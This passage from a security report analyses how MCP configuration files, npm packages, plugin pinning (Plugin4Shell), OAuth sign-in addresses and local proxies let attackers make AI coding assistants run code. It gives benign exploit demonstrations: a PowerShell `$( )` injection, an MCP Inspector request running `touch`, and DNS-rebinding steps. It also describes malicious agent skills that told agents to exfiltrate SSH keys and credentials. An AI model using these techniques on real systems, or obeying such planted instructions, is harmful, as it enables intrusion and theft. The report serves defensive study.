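OpenAI objected that repeated prompts could tire users until they approve everything. Mindgard answered that a project's server list rarely changes, so there would be few extra prompts. Neither side offers measurements, but Cursor and VS Code already ask for approval again after a change, which suggests that the extra prompts are tolerable. Codex is close to having the same check because, according to Mindgard, it already calculates a fingerprint of the project's configuration but doesn't use it to cancel an old approval.

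Breen proposes that Claude Code hash `.mcp.json`, `settings.json` and similar files when the user trusts the folder, and prompt the user again if any of them changes. Until Claude Code does something like this, a maintainer can look for these files in the pull request on GitHub's website before checking out the branch. `claude mcp reset-project-choices` clears earlier server approvals, but it may not help if a settings file on the branch approves the server again.

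### The same file on a build server

Nobody is present on a build server to answer an approval prompt. Anthropic warns in its documentation that Claude Code loads a project's servers without asking when it runs non-interactively, for example with `claude -p`.

Claude Code's GitHub Action had a more serious version of this problem, CVE-2026-47751. The Action runs Claude Code on GitHub's automation service, often to review pull requests. GitHub Advisory Database's *GHSA-8q5r-mmjf-575q* (2026) traces the flaw to a combination of three behaviours:

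1. The Action checked out the pull request's branch, so the attacker controlled the files in the working folder.
2. Claude Code read `.mcp.json` from that folder.
3. The Action always turned on `enableAllProjectMcpServers`, which approves every server in the file.

An attacker could open a pull request with a malicious `.mcp.json` and wait for the Action to run. The Action started when a user with the necessary permissions called on Claude, for instance in a comment, or automatically if the project had configured it that way. The attacker's command then ran on the build server and could read the secrets available to that job, such as API keys.

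Tenable's *Anthropic Claude Code Action Runner Arbitrary Code Execution* (2026) records that the security company reported the flaw on 12 February. An automated account on the bug-reporting platform first replied that it was a configuration issue. After Tenable objected, Anthropic reopened the report and eventually rated the flaw medium severity.

The advisory lists 1.0.74 as the fixed version, but Tenable lists 1.0.78, so 1.0.78 or later is the safer choice. Tenable confirmed on 25 March that the fix seemed to work. Projects that referred to the Action by a moving label such as `@v1` received the fix automatically, but those pinned to an older version had to update it themselves.

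According to OSV's *CVE-2026-47751* (2026), the Action now restores `.mcp.json` and the `.claude/` folder before Claude Code starts, using the copies from the base branch, which is the branch the pull request proposes to change. It doesn't need a prompt because the maintainers already control that branch. The Action also treats the stranger's configuration as untrusted, as Breen wanted Claude Code to do on a laptop.

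The fix protects the configuration but not every file it names. If the base branch contains Maria's original `helper` entry, the Action restores the entry, but `tools/helper.py` still comes from the pull request. An attacker could presumably leave `.mcp.json` alone and change the script. Projects that use the Action should avoid servers whose code is in the same repository, or install that code from somewhere a pull request can't change.

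### How direnv and VS Code tasks handle the same problem

Other developer tools have run commands from project files for years. One of them, direnv, sets environment variables when a user enters a folder in the terminal. It reads them from `.envrc`, a shell script that can run any command, so it blocks a new `.envrc` until the user types `direnv allow`. direnv's *unclutter your .profile* warns that without this step, any repository a user downloaded could wipe their hard drive when they entered its folder.

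direnv ties this permission to a hash of the file, so any edit blocks it again. Hirschberg (2026), in *If “stdio” is a Vulnerability, So Is “git clone”*, calls this the right model for MCP. Hirschberg, a co-founder of the security company ARMO, is otherwise critical of the attention on MCP because many older tools also turn configuration into commands.

VS Code applies a looser rule to tasks, which are commands stored in `.vscode/tasks.json` that a project can set to run whenever somebody opens the folder. It asks once whether the user trusts the folder, then runs later changes to the task without asking again. Users can decline and work in Restricted Mode, but this also disables agents, according to Visual Studio Code's *Workspace Trust*. A reviewer who wants an agent's help therefore has to trust the folder first.

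| Product | What the approval covers | Does a changed command need new approval? |
|---|---|---|
| direnv | The contents of `.envrc` | Yes |
| VS Code tasks | The folder | No |
| VS Code MCP servers | The server's configuration | Yes |
| Cursor before 1.3 | The server's name | No |
| Cursor 1.3 | The server's configuration | Yes |
| Claude Code 2.1.63 | The server's name | No |
| Codex CLI and Gemini CLI, as Mindgard tested them | The folder | No |

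In a real attack campaign that Microsoft described and Datadog cites, fake recruiters persuaded developers to download a project for a job interview and trust it in VS Code, which then ran a malicious task. A hash would not have protected these victims, because it only guards against changes made after approval, and the project was already malicious when they first approved it.

### What a configuration hash misses

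A hash of the launch configuration covers the text of the entry, so the program it starts can change without changing the hash. If a pull request edits only `tools/helper.py`, Maria's `helper` entry keeps the same hash and the assistant runs the new script without asking. The same happens if an `npx` entry doesn't specify a version and the package changes.

Codex asks users to approve hooks, which are commands that an assistant runs at set moments, such as the start of a session. Datadog reports that Codex hashes the exact definition of each hook and asks again if it changes, but does not check the contents of the scripts that the definition names. A script can therefore change after approval without Codex asking again.

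Changing an environment variable can also change what an entry starts. According to Anthropic's documentation, `.mcp.json` can contain references such as `${VAR}` in `command` and `args`, which Claude Code replaces with the variable's current value. The file and its hash stay the same when that value changes. An application can detect such a change by hashing the entry after filling in the values.

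Settings outside the entry can also change which program runs. Datadog's researchers used `.claude/settings.json` to put a folder from the repository at the front of `PATH`. When Claude Code called `git` to collect information about the project, it ran the repository's own script instead. The attack used no MCP server, so a hash of `.mcp.json` alone would not have caught it.

direnv's developers have had to deal with the same gap. The function reference from direnv (2019) warns that when an approved `.envrc` loads another `.envrc`, direnv does not check the second file. Since version 2.38.0, a project's author can use `require_allowed` to list additional files whose changes also require new approval. The manual recommends this for lockfiles, which record the exact versions of a project's packages, if the project runs code from those packages.

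Mindgard wants coding assistants to find such files automatically and include any script the configuration names. This would catch the change to `tools/helper.py`. But the script may import other modules or download code when it runs, and an assistant can't reliably find all of this code in advance.

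## Poisoned registries, packages and plugins

Maria's filesystem entry names a package that somebody else maintains. She can read and approve the entry without knowing what the package contains, and the maintainers can publish a new version at any time. An attacker who controls the package, or who persuades Maria to install a similar one, doesn't need to change her configuration.

Agents get their add-ons from several kinds of catalogue. npm stores the packages themselves, while sites such as mcp.so mostly list MCP servers and link to code on GitHub. Coding assistants also have marketplaces for plugins, which can add commands, scripts and MCP servers in one installation. Other catalogues offer skills, which are written instructions for a task.

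### From a package name to a running process

Consider this entry for an invented server:

```json
{
  "command": "npx",
  "args": ["-y", "example-notes-server"]
}
```

When the client uses it, the launch goes through these stages:

1. The client starts `npx` with the two arguments.
2. `npx` looks for a copy of the package in the current project and in its own cache, which holds packages from earlier launches.
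3. If it finds no copy, it requests the package's record from npm. The record lists every published version and has a label, `latest`, that points to one of them. The maintainer controls the label.
4. `npx` downloads that version and the other packages it depends on, without asking because of `-y`. A package can also include scripts that run during installation, if npm's settings allow them.
5. `npx` starts the program inside the package, and the client attempts the MCP handshake.

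npm compares each download with a hash in the registry's record. A match shows that the file arrived as the publisher uploaded it, but a malicious upload matches its own hash too.

If `npx` finds a cached copy, it may run that copy without looking for a newer one. Setup instructions often avoid this by adding a tag, as in `example-notes-server@latest`. Li and Gao (2025), in *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol*, point out that `npx` then retrieves the newest version every time it runs. This gives users bug fixes automatically, but it would also give them a malicious update.

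A pinned entry names one version, such as `example-notes-server@1.4.2`. npm doesn't let publishers replace the contents of a version they have published, so a later update can't reach this entry. The pin doesn't help if version 1.4.2 was malicious from the start. It may not cover the package's dependencies either, because most packages accept a range of versions for each dependency. A fresh installation of version 1.4.2 can therefore include a dependency published yesterday. To prevent this, a user can install the server with a lockfile that fixes the version of every package, then launch the installed copy.

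In *Same Name, Different Server*, Kraishan (2026) scanned the source code of 14,353 MCP servers and flagged 425 of them (3%) for unpinned or unverified dependencies. A manual check confirmed 39 of 42 such findings. The scanner seems to have looked mainly for dependencies with no version limit, so the share of servers whose dependencies can change is probably much higher.

### Code that turned malicious after people installed it

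In September 2025, a malicious update to the npm package `postmark-mcp` needed only one new line of code to blind-copy every email to an outsider. The package let agents send email through Postmark, an email delivery service, but the company behind Postmark had not published it. The early versions worked as users expected. The malicious version, 1.0.16, still delivered each email to its intended recipient.

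The update changed nothing in the users' launch configurations and started no suspicious program. Even a sandbox might not have stopped the copying, because the server needed to contact Postmark to send email and the copies left by the same route. Users who had pinned an earlier version would have avoided it.

A larger campaign on skills.sh, a public registry for skills, used the same delay. According to TechRadar's *Experts warn malicious AI skills are hitting more victims than ever*, Zenity Labs found that attackers had cloned existing skills under similar names and kept the copies harmless while they gained users. The attackers then added instructions for the agent to collect SSH keys, cloud credentials and other secrets and send them away. One family of skills had more than 1.7 million installs, though one person can account for many of them. Zenity could not determine how many people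 lost data.

A malicious skill doesn't have to change a launch configuration either; it works more like prompt injection that the user has installed on purpose. Microsoft and Vercel, which runs skills.sh, removed the skills that Zenity identified, but copies stay on users' machines until users delete them. Zenity also found hundreds of empty packages whose names somebody had apparently reserved for later attacks.

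Scanning can miss such add-ons. In June, Constantin (2026) reported in *A fake AI agent skill passed every security scanner* that a test skill built by the security company AIR had passed scanners from Cisco and NVIDIA. By AIR's count, the skill reached 26,000 agents. AIR later wrote that it had "seized control" of them, but Constantin describes the skill as harmless, so the figure is better evidence of how far an unknown publisher's skill can spread than of damage. A scanner also checks only the version it receives. The first versions of the skills on skills.sh did nothing malicious, so even a perfect scanner would have passed them.

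### What registries accept

OX Security reports that it "poisoned" 9 out of 11 MCP registries with a "malicious trial balloon", which presumably means that those registries published its test entry. OX's summary omits the entry's contents, the names of the registries, the checks they applied and the reason the attempt failed at the other two. It also reports no installations.

The trial therefore shows only that OX could get a listing in most of the registries it tried. An attacker would still need people to find the entry among thousands of others and install it. The skills.sh campaign is better evidence that people install lookalikes.

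Li and Gao give more detail on how weak the checks were in 2025. Between late June and early July, they collected 67,057 listings from six registries. They chose five from a list of 27 MCP registries: mcp.so, MCP Market, MCP Store, Pulse MCP and Smithery. The sixth was npm, a general package registry, where they kept packages that had "mcp" in the name and depended on a known MCP library. The total may count the same server more than once, because a server can be listed in several registries.

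The researchers found four ways for an attacker to take over a server's identity or imitate it:

| Weakness | What Li and Gao found | What an attacker could do |
|---|---|---|
| Deleted GitHub accounts | 212 listings with an account name that anyone could register | Register the name and recreate the server |
| Renamed GitHub accounts | 304 old account names that anyone could register | Register the old name and take over links to it |
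| Published passwords | 9 GitHub tokens in 5,659 sample configurations, 5 of them still valid | Change the code in the owner's repositories |
| Similar names on npm | 408 groups of packages whose names differ only in parts such as `-mcp` or `-mcp-server` | Publish a lookalike |

GitHub makes a deleted account's name available again after 90 days. When a developer renames an account, GitHub redirects links from the old name to the new one. The redirection ends if somebody else registers the old name and creates a repository with the same name as the original. An entry that runs `npx -y github:old-name/notes-server` would then download the new owner's code, even though the entry has not changed.

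The deleted and renamed accounts together affect about 1% of the 52,539 listings on the four registries that link to code elsewhere. Li and Gao checked whether the names were free but did not register any, so they did not test a full takeover.

The tokens came from developers who misunderstood a sample configuration on mcp.so. The sample was for GitHub's own MCP server, which needs a token, but some developers of unrelated servers pasted in their own tokens. When Li and Gao collected the data again later, they found only one token, and it had expired.

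Different developers maintained the packages in 80.6% of the 408 groups with similar names. This shows how easily a user could pick the wrong package. It doesn't measure how many packages are fraudulent, because two people can independently write a server for the same service and give it an obvious name.

Li and Gao also scanned server code and found 833 servers with exploitable flaws, such as a tool that runs its input as Python code. They checked 41 by hand and confirmed 37. The flaws are mostly programming mistakes. Another 18 servers had suspicious tool descriptions, but most of those were demonstrations. The study is strong evidence that attackers had flaws to exploit in 2025, but weak evidence that many had exploited them.

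### How servers in the official registry change

Kraishan's census covers the official MCP registry, which was not among Li and Gao's six. The August 2026 snapshot contains 21,643 servers and 72,606 version records. Kraishan compared successive records for the 8,900 servers that had published more than one version, so the census can show how long a description of a server stays accurate.

Of these, 51.1% had changed their description, packages or remote addresses. Kraishan classes 40.6% as having changed silently, meaning that every identifier stayed the same while the meaning or destination changed. However, any rewritten description counts as a silent change, and 3,242 of the roughly 3,600 servers in this group had rewritten theirs. Many of those edits were probably corrections or better explanations.

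Changes to the packages matter more for local launches. Among the servers with several versions, 11.1% added a package, 9.4% removed one, and 3.5% changed the runtime hint, a field that suggests which program should run the package. Thirteen servers moved to a different package registry. Someone who installs a server after such a change may get a different launch command from someone who installed it earlier, even though the server's name is the same.

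Another 370 servers (4.2%) moved their remote address to a different host. Kraishan expects that most of these moves were routine and doesn't claim that any were malicious. But neither the registry nor an MCP client can distinguish a routine move from a takeover, and the protocol doesn't notify users who have already installed the server of the move.

Among the servers that changed at all, the median time to the first change was zero days. Kraishan goes too far in concluding that a typical server has already changed by the end of the day on which a user reviews it, because the figure leaves out servers that never changed. It also presumably counts from the day the developer first published the server, when developers often correct small mistakes. A user who installs the server months later may find it much more stable.

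The census also can't detect changes like the one in `postmark-mcp`. The registry doesn't record which tools a server offers, and the server's code is in a different registry. If a maintainer added a blind copy to every email, at most the version number in the registry's record would change.

Kraishan's scan of the source code found no hidden instructions in the tool descriptions of any of the 14,353 servers, though the scanner matches known patterns and would miss disguised text. The result suggests that undisguised versions of this attack, which researchers have demonstrated many times, were rare in the official registry.

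### How Plugin4Shell got around pinning

Pinning an npm version works because npm won't change a version once it is published. Plugins for coding assistants usually come from Git repositories, where a branch can point to new code at any time. Marketplaces therefore pin a plugin to a commit, a saved snapshot of the project that Git identifies by a hash, usually written as 40 characters. The marketplace reviews the snapshot and records its hash, and the assistant should install exactly that snapshot.

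A poisoned plugin can do a great deal of damage. Red Hat (2026) warns that Claude Code plugins run without a sandbox and with all the user's permissions. The user approves the installation once, not each command, script and MCP server inside the plugin. Red Hat also describes plugins installed without a pin, so reinstalling one fetches whatever is on the repository's default branch at that moment.

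On 17 September 2026, AIR published a way to bypass commit pinning. According to AIR's *Plugin4Shell*, Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI all requested the pinned commit but never checked which commit they received.

In the first three products, the attack depends on names. Constantin (2026), in *Plugin4Shell*, explains that Git lets a branch have a name that looks exactly like a commit hash. If a name matches both a branch and a commit, the checkout uses the branch. An attacker who controls a plugin's repository can exploit this as follows:

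1. The attacker publishes a harmless commit, and the marketplace reviews it and pins its hash.
2. The attacker creates a branch with that hash as its name, points the branch at different code and makes it the repository's default branch.
3. The assistant downloads the repository. Git automatically sets up the default branch on the user's machine.
4. The assistant runs `git checkout` with the pinned hash. Git finds the branch of that name and loads the attacker's code.
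5. The assistant reports that it has installed the pinned commit.

A harmless test could add an MCP server whose command is `touch` to the code on the branch. The command would create an empty file when the assistant started the plugin's servers, even though the marketplace had reviewed a version without that command.

Gemini CLI first used the hash to download the right commit. It then loaded the files using the name `FETCH_HEAD`, which normally refers to whatever Git has just downloaded. If the attacker had named the repository's default branch `FETCH_HEAD`, Git loaded that branch instead.

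The same check stops both attacks. After the checkout, the assistant finds out which commit is actually in the folder and stops if it differs from the pin. As a shell command, the check could look like this:

```
test "$(git rev-parse HEAD)" = "$PINNED_HASH" || exit 1
```

`git rev-parse HEAD` prints the full hash of the current commit. The assistant has to compare this with the pinned hash before it starts anything from the plugin. An attacker can give a branch any name the host allows, but can't make different code match the pinned hash.

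#### Who was exposed

AIR calls the flaw "zero-click" because Claude Code and Codex update plugins in the background by default, according to Help Net Security's *Zero-click RCE vulnerability hit four major AI coding agents, two remain unpatched* (2026). When the marketplace moves the pin to a newer commit, the assistant repeats the checkout, and the attacker's code can replace a plugin that the user installed long ago. The victim does nothing, but the attacker has to wait for the pin to move. An attacker who maintains the plugin can prompt this by submitting a harmless update for review.

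The attacker also needs control of the repository. They can publish a useful plugin and make it malicious later, as in the skills.sh campaign, or take over someone else's repository. AIR reports that the maintainers of 925 skills already in use had lost them to repository takeovers, which affected 134,000 agents. AIR presents these takeovers and the pin bypass as a chain proven end to end. However, it demonstrated the parts separately, and the takeovers it counted were of skills, whereas the bypass applies to pinned plugins.

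Bitbucket and self-hosted Git servers allow branch names that look like full commit hashes, but GitHub refuses them, which protects plugins hosted there from the attack on Claude Code, Codex and Copilot. AIR therefore overstates the exposure when it says that anyone who installs marketplace plugins in these products is exposed. Its headline figure of "millions of agents" probably reflects how many people use the products. The GitHub rule does not protect Gemini CLI, because `FETCH_HEAD` doesn't look like a hash.

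GitHub responded to the report by pointing to its naming rule, according to IlSoftware.it's *Plugin4Shell, falla zero-click negli agenti AI*. AIR answered that Copilot also supports repositories on other hosts. A marketplace could accept only plugins from GitHub, but it would then exclude hosts that the assistants officially support. AIR sells a marketplace and a filter for add-ons and advertises that neither was affected, so it has a commercial interest in the matter. It still makes a sound technical argument that the assistant has to check the files because it chooses which ones to load.

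AIR found the flaw in May 2026, built working exploits for all four products and informed the vendors in June.

| Product | Status when last reported, in September 2026 | What users can do |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | Fixed in 2.1.179 | Update |
| Codex | Fixed in 0.146.0 | Update |
| GitHub Copilot | No fix released | Install plugins only from repositories on GitHub, and check the release notes for a later fix |
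| Gemini CLI | No fix planned, because Google is retiring the product | Move to Antigravity, the replacement Google recommends |

Updating stops the assistant from accepting the wrong commit in future. Users who installed plugins from other hosts before updating should also compare the installed commit with the marketplace's pin, or delete the plugin and install it again.

### What an official registry can prove

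OX advises users to install MCP servers only from verified sources and gives "the official GitHub MCP Registry" as an example. GitHub's registry is separate from the official MCP registry that Kraishan studied, so a company that adopts this rule has to specify which one it means. OX's trial doesn't show how well the rule works, because the summary doesn't identify the two registries where the test entry failed.

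The official MCP registry checks that publishers control the names they use. Publishing under `io.github.maria/` requires signing in to the GitHub account `maria`, and publishing under a name based on a web domain requires proving control of that domain. Users can therefore reliably tell a company's own server from an imitation. The publisher of `postmark-mcp`, for example, could not have used a name based on Postmark's domain.

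The check helps only users who know which publisher to expect. The same author could have registered a personal GitHub name and truthfully listed the package under it. Someone who searched for "postmark" and chose the first result might still have installed it.

An identity check also can't detect when a publisher starts releasing malicious code. The person who controlled `postmark-mcp` when it was harmless also published the malicious version. If an attacker steals the publisher's account, the login is still valid. The registry stores only a description of each server and a reference to its package, so an attacker with access to the publisher's npm account may not need to change the registry entry.

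Honest publishers can also release insecure servers by mistake. Kraishan's scanner flagged 11.1% of the servers it examined in the official registry for at least one serious weakness, or about 7.6% after correction for false alarms. Most of these servers accepted network connections without proper authentication. A project's number of GitHub stars showed almost no correlation with the number of weaknesses found, although the most popular tenth of servers did somewhat better than the rest.

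With provenance attestation, the service that builds a package signs a record of the exact source code it used. Users can then confirm that the package on npm was built from the public source, which would expose an altered package that an attacker uploaded with a stolen npm password. Somebody would still have to read the source to find any malicious code in it. Kraishan reports that the MCP ecosystem still largely lacks provenance records, signing and automatic malware checks.

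Kraishan recommends that registries record each server's tools and publish machine-readable differences between versions. Until they do, an MCP client can store a hash of the package on first use and alert the user when it changes. This would have alerted users that `postmark-mcp` had changed, but not that the update was malicious.

A company can go further by reviewing one version, keeping its own copy of the package and all its dependencies, and launching only that copy. The company then has to track security fixes itself.

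## Remote servers and web pages that trigger a local launch

A company can avoid running other people's packages by choosing remote servers, because the client has no server to start. But many remote servers require users to sign in, for which the client normally has to open a browser on the user's computer.

### How signing in starts a local program

MCP uses OAuth for signing in. The process begins like this:

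1. The client contacts the server, which refuses the request and asks for a sign-in.
2. The client downloads a description of the server's sign-in system. One field, `authorization_endpoint`, gives the address of the sign-in page.
3. The client adds a few details to the address, such as the type of reply it expects.
4. The client opens the address in a browser, where the user signs in.

The server's operator writes the address in step 2. Obsidian Security's *From well-known to Well-Pwned* explains that desktop and command-line clients have to launch a browser process to show the page, so a malicious operator controls text that the client passes to another program.

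A client can safely pass the address as a single argument, without a shell. On Windows, however, some clients paste it into a line for PowerShell, one of the Windows shells:

```powershell
Start-Process "https://example.com/$(Get-Date)"
```

PowerShell runs any command inside `$( )` in a double-quoted string. Here it runs `Get-Date`, a harmless command that returns the time, and puts the result into the address before opening the browser. It would run a command that creates an empty file in the same way.

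This mistake is older than MCP. GitHub Security Lab's *GHSL-2020-145* (2020) describes it in Opener, a JavaScript package that opened links through `cmd.exe`. *OS command injection on windows when opening urls*, a 2023 user report by tripodsan, describes the same problem with PowerShell in a similar package, `open`. The maintainer replied that `open` makes no security guarantees and that developers must clean untrusted input themselves.

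### OpenCode's flaw

OpenCode, an open-source coding assistant from Anomaly, used an old version of `open`. Pillar Security disclosed the resulting flaw on 19 October 2026. According to The Hacker News' *OpenCode Flaw Lets Malicious MCP Servers Execute Code During Sign-In* (2026), the flaw affects versions 1.0.137 to 1.18.32 on Windows and on the Windows Subsystem for Linux, which runs Linux programs inside Windows. On macOS and ordinary Linux, OpenCode opens the browser without a shell.

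The attack works only if the developer has added a remote server that the attacker controls and then starts the sign-in, for example with `opencode mcp auth`. Adding the server or opening a session is not enough. Pillar proposed a severity score of 9.8 out of 10, which seems high because scores that high are normally for attacks that need no action from the victim.

Accepting only addresses that begin with `https://` is a common defence that doesn't block the address in the PowerShell example, which begins that way too. PowerShell interprets the whole address, including the part after `https://` that the check doesn't cover.

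Anomaly fixed the flaw in version 1.18.33 on 28 September. The release added a check on how the address begins. But the important change, according to *Researchers Warn OpenCode Quietly Patched Critical RCE Flaw* (Poireault, 2026), was a newer version of `open`, which quotes the address so that PowerShell treats it as plain text. Pillar advises developers to go further and pass untrusted addresses as arguments, without a shell.

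#### Is a malicious server part of the threat model?

Pillar had reported the flaw privately on 29 August and later asked Anomaly to request a CVE. Anomaly declined because it considers malicious MCP servers outside its threat model, the set of attacks a product is meant to withstand. Its security policy puts any MCP server the user configures "outside our trust boundary".

That position makes sense for a local server. Starting one already lets its code run with the user's privileges, so a flaw that lets the server run commands adds little to what it can do. But a user who adds a remote server has agreed only to exchange data with it. Similarly, the MCP project's policy on security reports does not count it as a vulnerability if one side of a stdio connection can merely crash the other, but the report stays in scope if an attacker can reach the same code over a remote transport.

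A server that was a sensible choice when the user added it can also become malicious later, if an attacker breaks into it or buys its expired domain.

Anomaly fixed the flaw anyway, so the practical disagreement was about whether to tell users. The code change was labelled a refactor, and neither it nor the release notes mentioned security. Without a CVE, vulnerability scanners don't flag the old versions, so administrators have to check the version number on each machine. Anomaly has published advisories for other OpenCode flaws this year, which makes its silence about this one harder to justify.

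### The same flaw in mcp-remote a year earlier

JFrog's *Critical RCE Vulnerability in mcp-remote* (2025) describes almost the same flaw, CVE-2025-6514. mcp-remote is a small program that lets clients that support only local servers connect to remote ones. A typical entry runs `npx` with the arguments `mcp-remote` and the server's address, so connecting involves a stdio launch even when the remote server is benign.

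mcp-remote also passed the sign-in address to `open`, but an attacker needed less from the victim than with OpenCode. Claude Desktop started mcp-remote when the user saved the configuration or restarted the application. mcp-remote then contacted the server, which could demand a sign-in immediately, so the user didn't have to enter a sign-in command.

The attack could also work through a legitimate server if the entry used an unencrypted `http` address, because someone on the same local network could intercept the connection and supply their own sign-in address.

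On Windows, JFrog found that a `file:` URL started a program already on the computer. An ordinary `http` URL containing `$( )` also started a program, but the client encoded any spaces, so JFrog couldn't add arguments. A URL with an invented scheme avoided the encoding and gave JFrog full control of the command. On macOS and Linux, a `file:` URL could start a program, but JFrog had little control over its arguments.

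Accepting only web addresses would have stopped the `file:` address and the invented prefix but not the `http` one. The encoded spaces are not a reliable barrier. Veria Labs' *From MCP to Shell* (2025) shows that an attacker can encode a whole command as text without spaces and have PowerShell decode it.

Veria Labs, a security company, used this method against Claude Code, which already checked that addresses began with `http://` or `https://`. An earlier version opened them through `cmd.exe`, where `&` starts a new command. Web addresses routinely use `&` to separate parameters, so a filter can't simply ban it.

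| Client | How it opened the address on Windows | Fix |
|---|---|---|
| mcp-remote 0.0.5 to 0.1.15 | PowerShell, through `open` | Fixed in 0.1.16 |
| Claude Code 1.0.53 | `cmd.exe` | 1.0.54 switched to PowerShell and was still vulnerable; a later version uses no shell |
| Gemini CLI, in July 2025 | PowerShell, through `open` | Google replaced `open` with its own code, which escapes quotation marks |
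| OpenCode 1.0.137 to 1.18.32 | PowerShell, through `open` | Fixed in 1.18.33 |

Anthropic's final fix for Claude Code is the strongest of those with published details, because it doesn't pass the address through a shell. Veria Labs considers Google's fix effective but less robust, because it depends on escaping the text correctly.

### How a web page reaches a program on the same computer

An attacker may not need an MCP server. A web page's scripts run in the browser on the visitor's own computer, and they can send requests to `127.0.0.1` (localhost), the address a computer uses for itself. A service that accepts connections only from the same machine will accept these requests, because the browser is on that machine.

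Under the same-origin policy, browsers let a page's script send simple requests to another site but normally don't let it read the replies. This protects private data, but it doesn't help if the request itself starts a program.

#### MCP Inspector

MCP Inspector, Anthropic's tool for testing MCP servers, is controlled from a web page. Because a web page can't start programs, the Inspector also runs a local proxy that launches stdio servers at the page's request. Before version 0.14.1, the proxy did not check who sent the request, so other web pages could also trigger a launch.

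Lumelsky (2025), in *Critical RCE Vulnerability in Anthropic MCP Inspector*, shows how the security company Oligo exploited this flaw, CVE-2025-49596. A malicious page only had to make the visitor's browser request an address like this:

```
http://0.0.0.0:6277/sse?transportType=stdio&command=touch&args=/tmp/launch-test
```

The proxy listened on port 6277. The rest of the request's address contained a launch configuration with a transport, a command and an argument. When the request arrived, the proxy ran `touch` and created an empty file, even though the page that sent the request couldn't read the reply.

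Developers could be running the Inspector without having chosen to, because the quickstart guide for the official Python library recommended `mcp dev`, which started the proxy in the background. A developer who then read a malicious blog post in the same browser could lose control of the machine.

Oligo used `0.0.0.0` because some browsers let public websites reach services on the visitor's machine through this address. Chromium and Firefox still allowed this in mid-2025. Strobes' *CVE-2026-22812*, a page about a different flaw, notes that Chrome 142 and later may ask for permission before a page contacts the local network, but Firefox does not.

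#### DNS rebinding

Oligo also reached the proxy by DNS rebinding, which lets the page read the replies as well. DNS is the system that translates a name such as `example.com` into a numerical address. The attack takes advantage of the fact that browsers identify a site by its name and port, not by its numerical address:

1. The victim opens a page at `http://attacker.example:6277`. DNS gives the address of the attacker's server, which delivers the page.
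2. The attacker changes the DNS record so that the name now points to `127.0.0.1`.
3. A script on the page sends another request to `attacker.example:6277`. The browser looks up the name again and connects to the victim's own computer.
4. The name and port haven't changed, so the browser treats the reply as coming from the same site and lets the script read it.

Recorded Future's *Anthropic MCP Inspector* gives the same explanation of how the attack bypasses the same-origin policy. Reading replies matters when a script has to take several steps, such as listing a server's tools before calling one.

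According to GitLab's *CVE-2025-9611* (2026), Microsoft's MCP server for Playwright was vulnerable to DNS rebinding before version 0.0.40, so a web page could call its tools. The attack used a server that was already running, so it didn't need to launch one.

Some local services can be attacked without DNS rebinding. Before version 1.0.216, OpenCode automatically started a local web server that needed no login and let any website read its replies. OSV's *CVE-2026-22812* (2026) records that a website could use this server to run shell commands. OpenCode users need 1.18.33 or later, because 1.0.216 still has the sign-in flaw. A crafted web page could also reach a local copy of GPT Researcher.

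#### The Inspector's fix and a way around it

Version 0.14.1 of the Inspector made the proxy require a session token, which an outside web page doesn't have, and check the `Host` and `Origin` headers. These headers contain the name the browser is contacting and the site that sent the request. DNS rebinding changes the IP address but not the name, so `attacker.example` still appears in the headers and the proxy can refuse the request.

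Both checks work only if the Inspector's own page is trustworthy. Veria Labs bypassed them with a malicious MCP server, using a flaw later numbered CVE-2025-58444. The server supplied a sign-in address beginning with `javascript:`, which makes a browser run the text that follows as a script. When the Inspector opened this address, the script ran as part of the Inspector's page. The script copied the session token from the page's own address and sent the proxy a request to start a program. The proxy started the program because the token was valid and the request came from the expected site.

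Anthropic responded by making the official TypeScript library reject `javascript:` and other dangerous prefixes, which also protected other clients that use the library. Developers should install a current version of the Inspector, not just 0.14.1, and check for old copies inside individual projects.

### The rules in the MCP documentation

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) documentation now has a rule for nearly every step in these attacks. Its security guidance covers sign-in addresses and proxies, and *Streamable HTTP* (2026) sets the rules for servers that accept web requests.

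| Rule | Link it breaks | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Clients must accept only `http` and `https` sign-in addresses, with `http` limited to local development | A `javascript:` address runs a script, or a `file:` address starts a program | A shell can run part of an `https` address |
| Clients must not use a shell to open an address | Part of the address becomes a command | A web-based client can still run a `javascript:` address |
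| Web-based clients should set a Content Security Policy, which limits the scripts a page may run | The browser runs the attacker's script in the client's page | Shell commands in the address |
| Servers must check the `Origin` header | Another website sends requests to a local server, directly or by DNS rebinding | Scripts inside the client's own page |
| Servers should require authentication | A caller without a token uses the server | A script that steals the token |
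| Proxies should sandbox the processes they start | The new process reaches the user's files and network | The process still starts |

Veria Labs found that ChatGPT passed a malicious server's address to the browser much as the Inspector did, but ChatGPT's Content Security Policy prevented the script from running.

The ban on shells would have prevented the OpenCode flaw, but a developer could easily miss it because it is in the separate security guidance. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026), part of the formal specification, requires HTTPS for sign-in addresses but does not cover how to open them. A developer who followed only that page could add the HTTPS check and still pass the address to PowerShell.

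The guidance also tells clients to reject addresses with characters that a shell could interpret. This is hard to follow literally because the client normally adds `&`, one of those characters, when it fills in the sign-in details. A client that opens the address without using a shell doesn't need this filter.

Local servers should also accept connections only from localhost. This blocks other machines on the network but not web pages, since the visitor's browser connects from the same machine.

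The guidance recommends that proxies log every stdio launch and require extra authorization for dangerous commands. A confirmation outside the web page would probably have stopped the attack on the Inspector's token, because a script in the page couldn't have clicked it. But the extra authorization is only recommended, and the developer has to decide which commands are dangerous. A program's name, such as `npx` or `python`, is a poor guide to that, so a proxy would do better to request confirmation before every new launch and show the full command.

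## Why closing one route leaves the others open

Anomaly's fix for OpenCode stops a malicious server from running a command through its sign-in address, but it doesn't protect developers from a poisoned package. Most of the patches described so far have this limit, because the vendor closed the path a researcher reported and left other ways to start a process.

### The routes as a graph

A graph, in the mathematical sense, is a set of points joined by links. In the graph below, the sources of untrusted input are on the left and the start of a new process is on the right. An attack works if it can follow links from one of those sources to the start of a new process.

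```
stranger      -> web form          -> launch entry -> SDK -> new process
text author   -> agent's file edit -> launch entry -> SDK -> new process
contributor   -> repository file   -> launch entry -> SDK -> new process
web page      -> local proxy       -> launch entry -> SDK -> new process
publisher     -> package -------------------------> SDK -> new process
remote server -> sign-in address   -> browser opener ----> new process
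```

A cut is a set of links whose removal separates every source from the new process, and the minimum cut is the smallest such set. A defender who works on the left has to remove six links, and one more whenever developers add a new way to configure servers. Further right, five of the paths go through the SDK's launch function and one goes through the code that opens a browser, so removing two links is enough. The minimum cut is a single link at the operating system. *AgentBouncer* (2026), for example, describes a system that checks an agent's requests to the operating system before the kernel carries them out.

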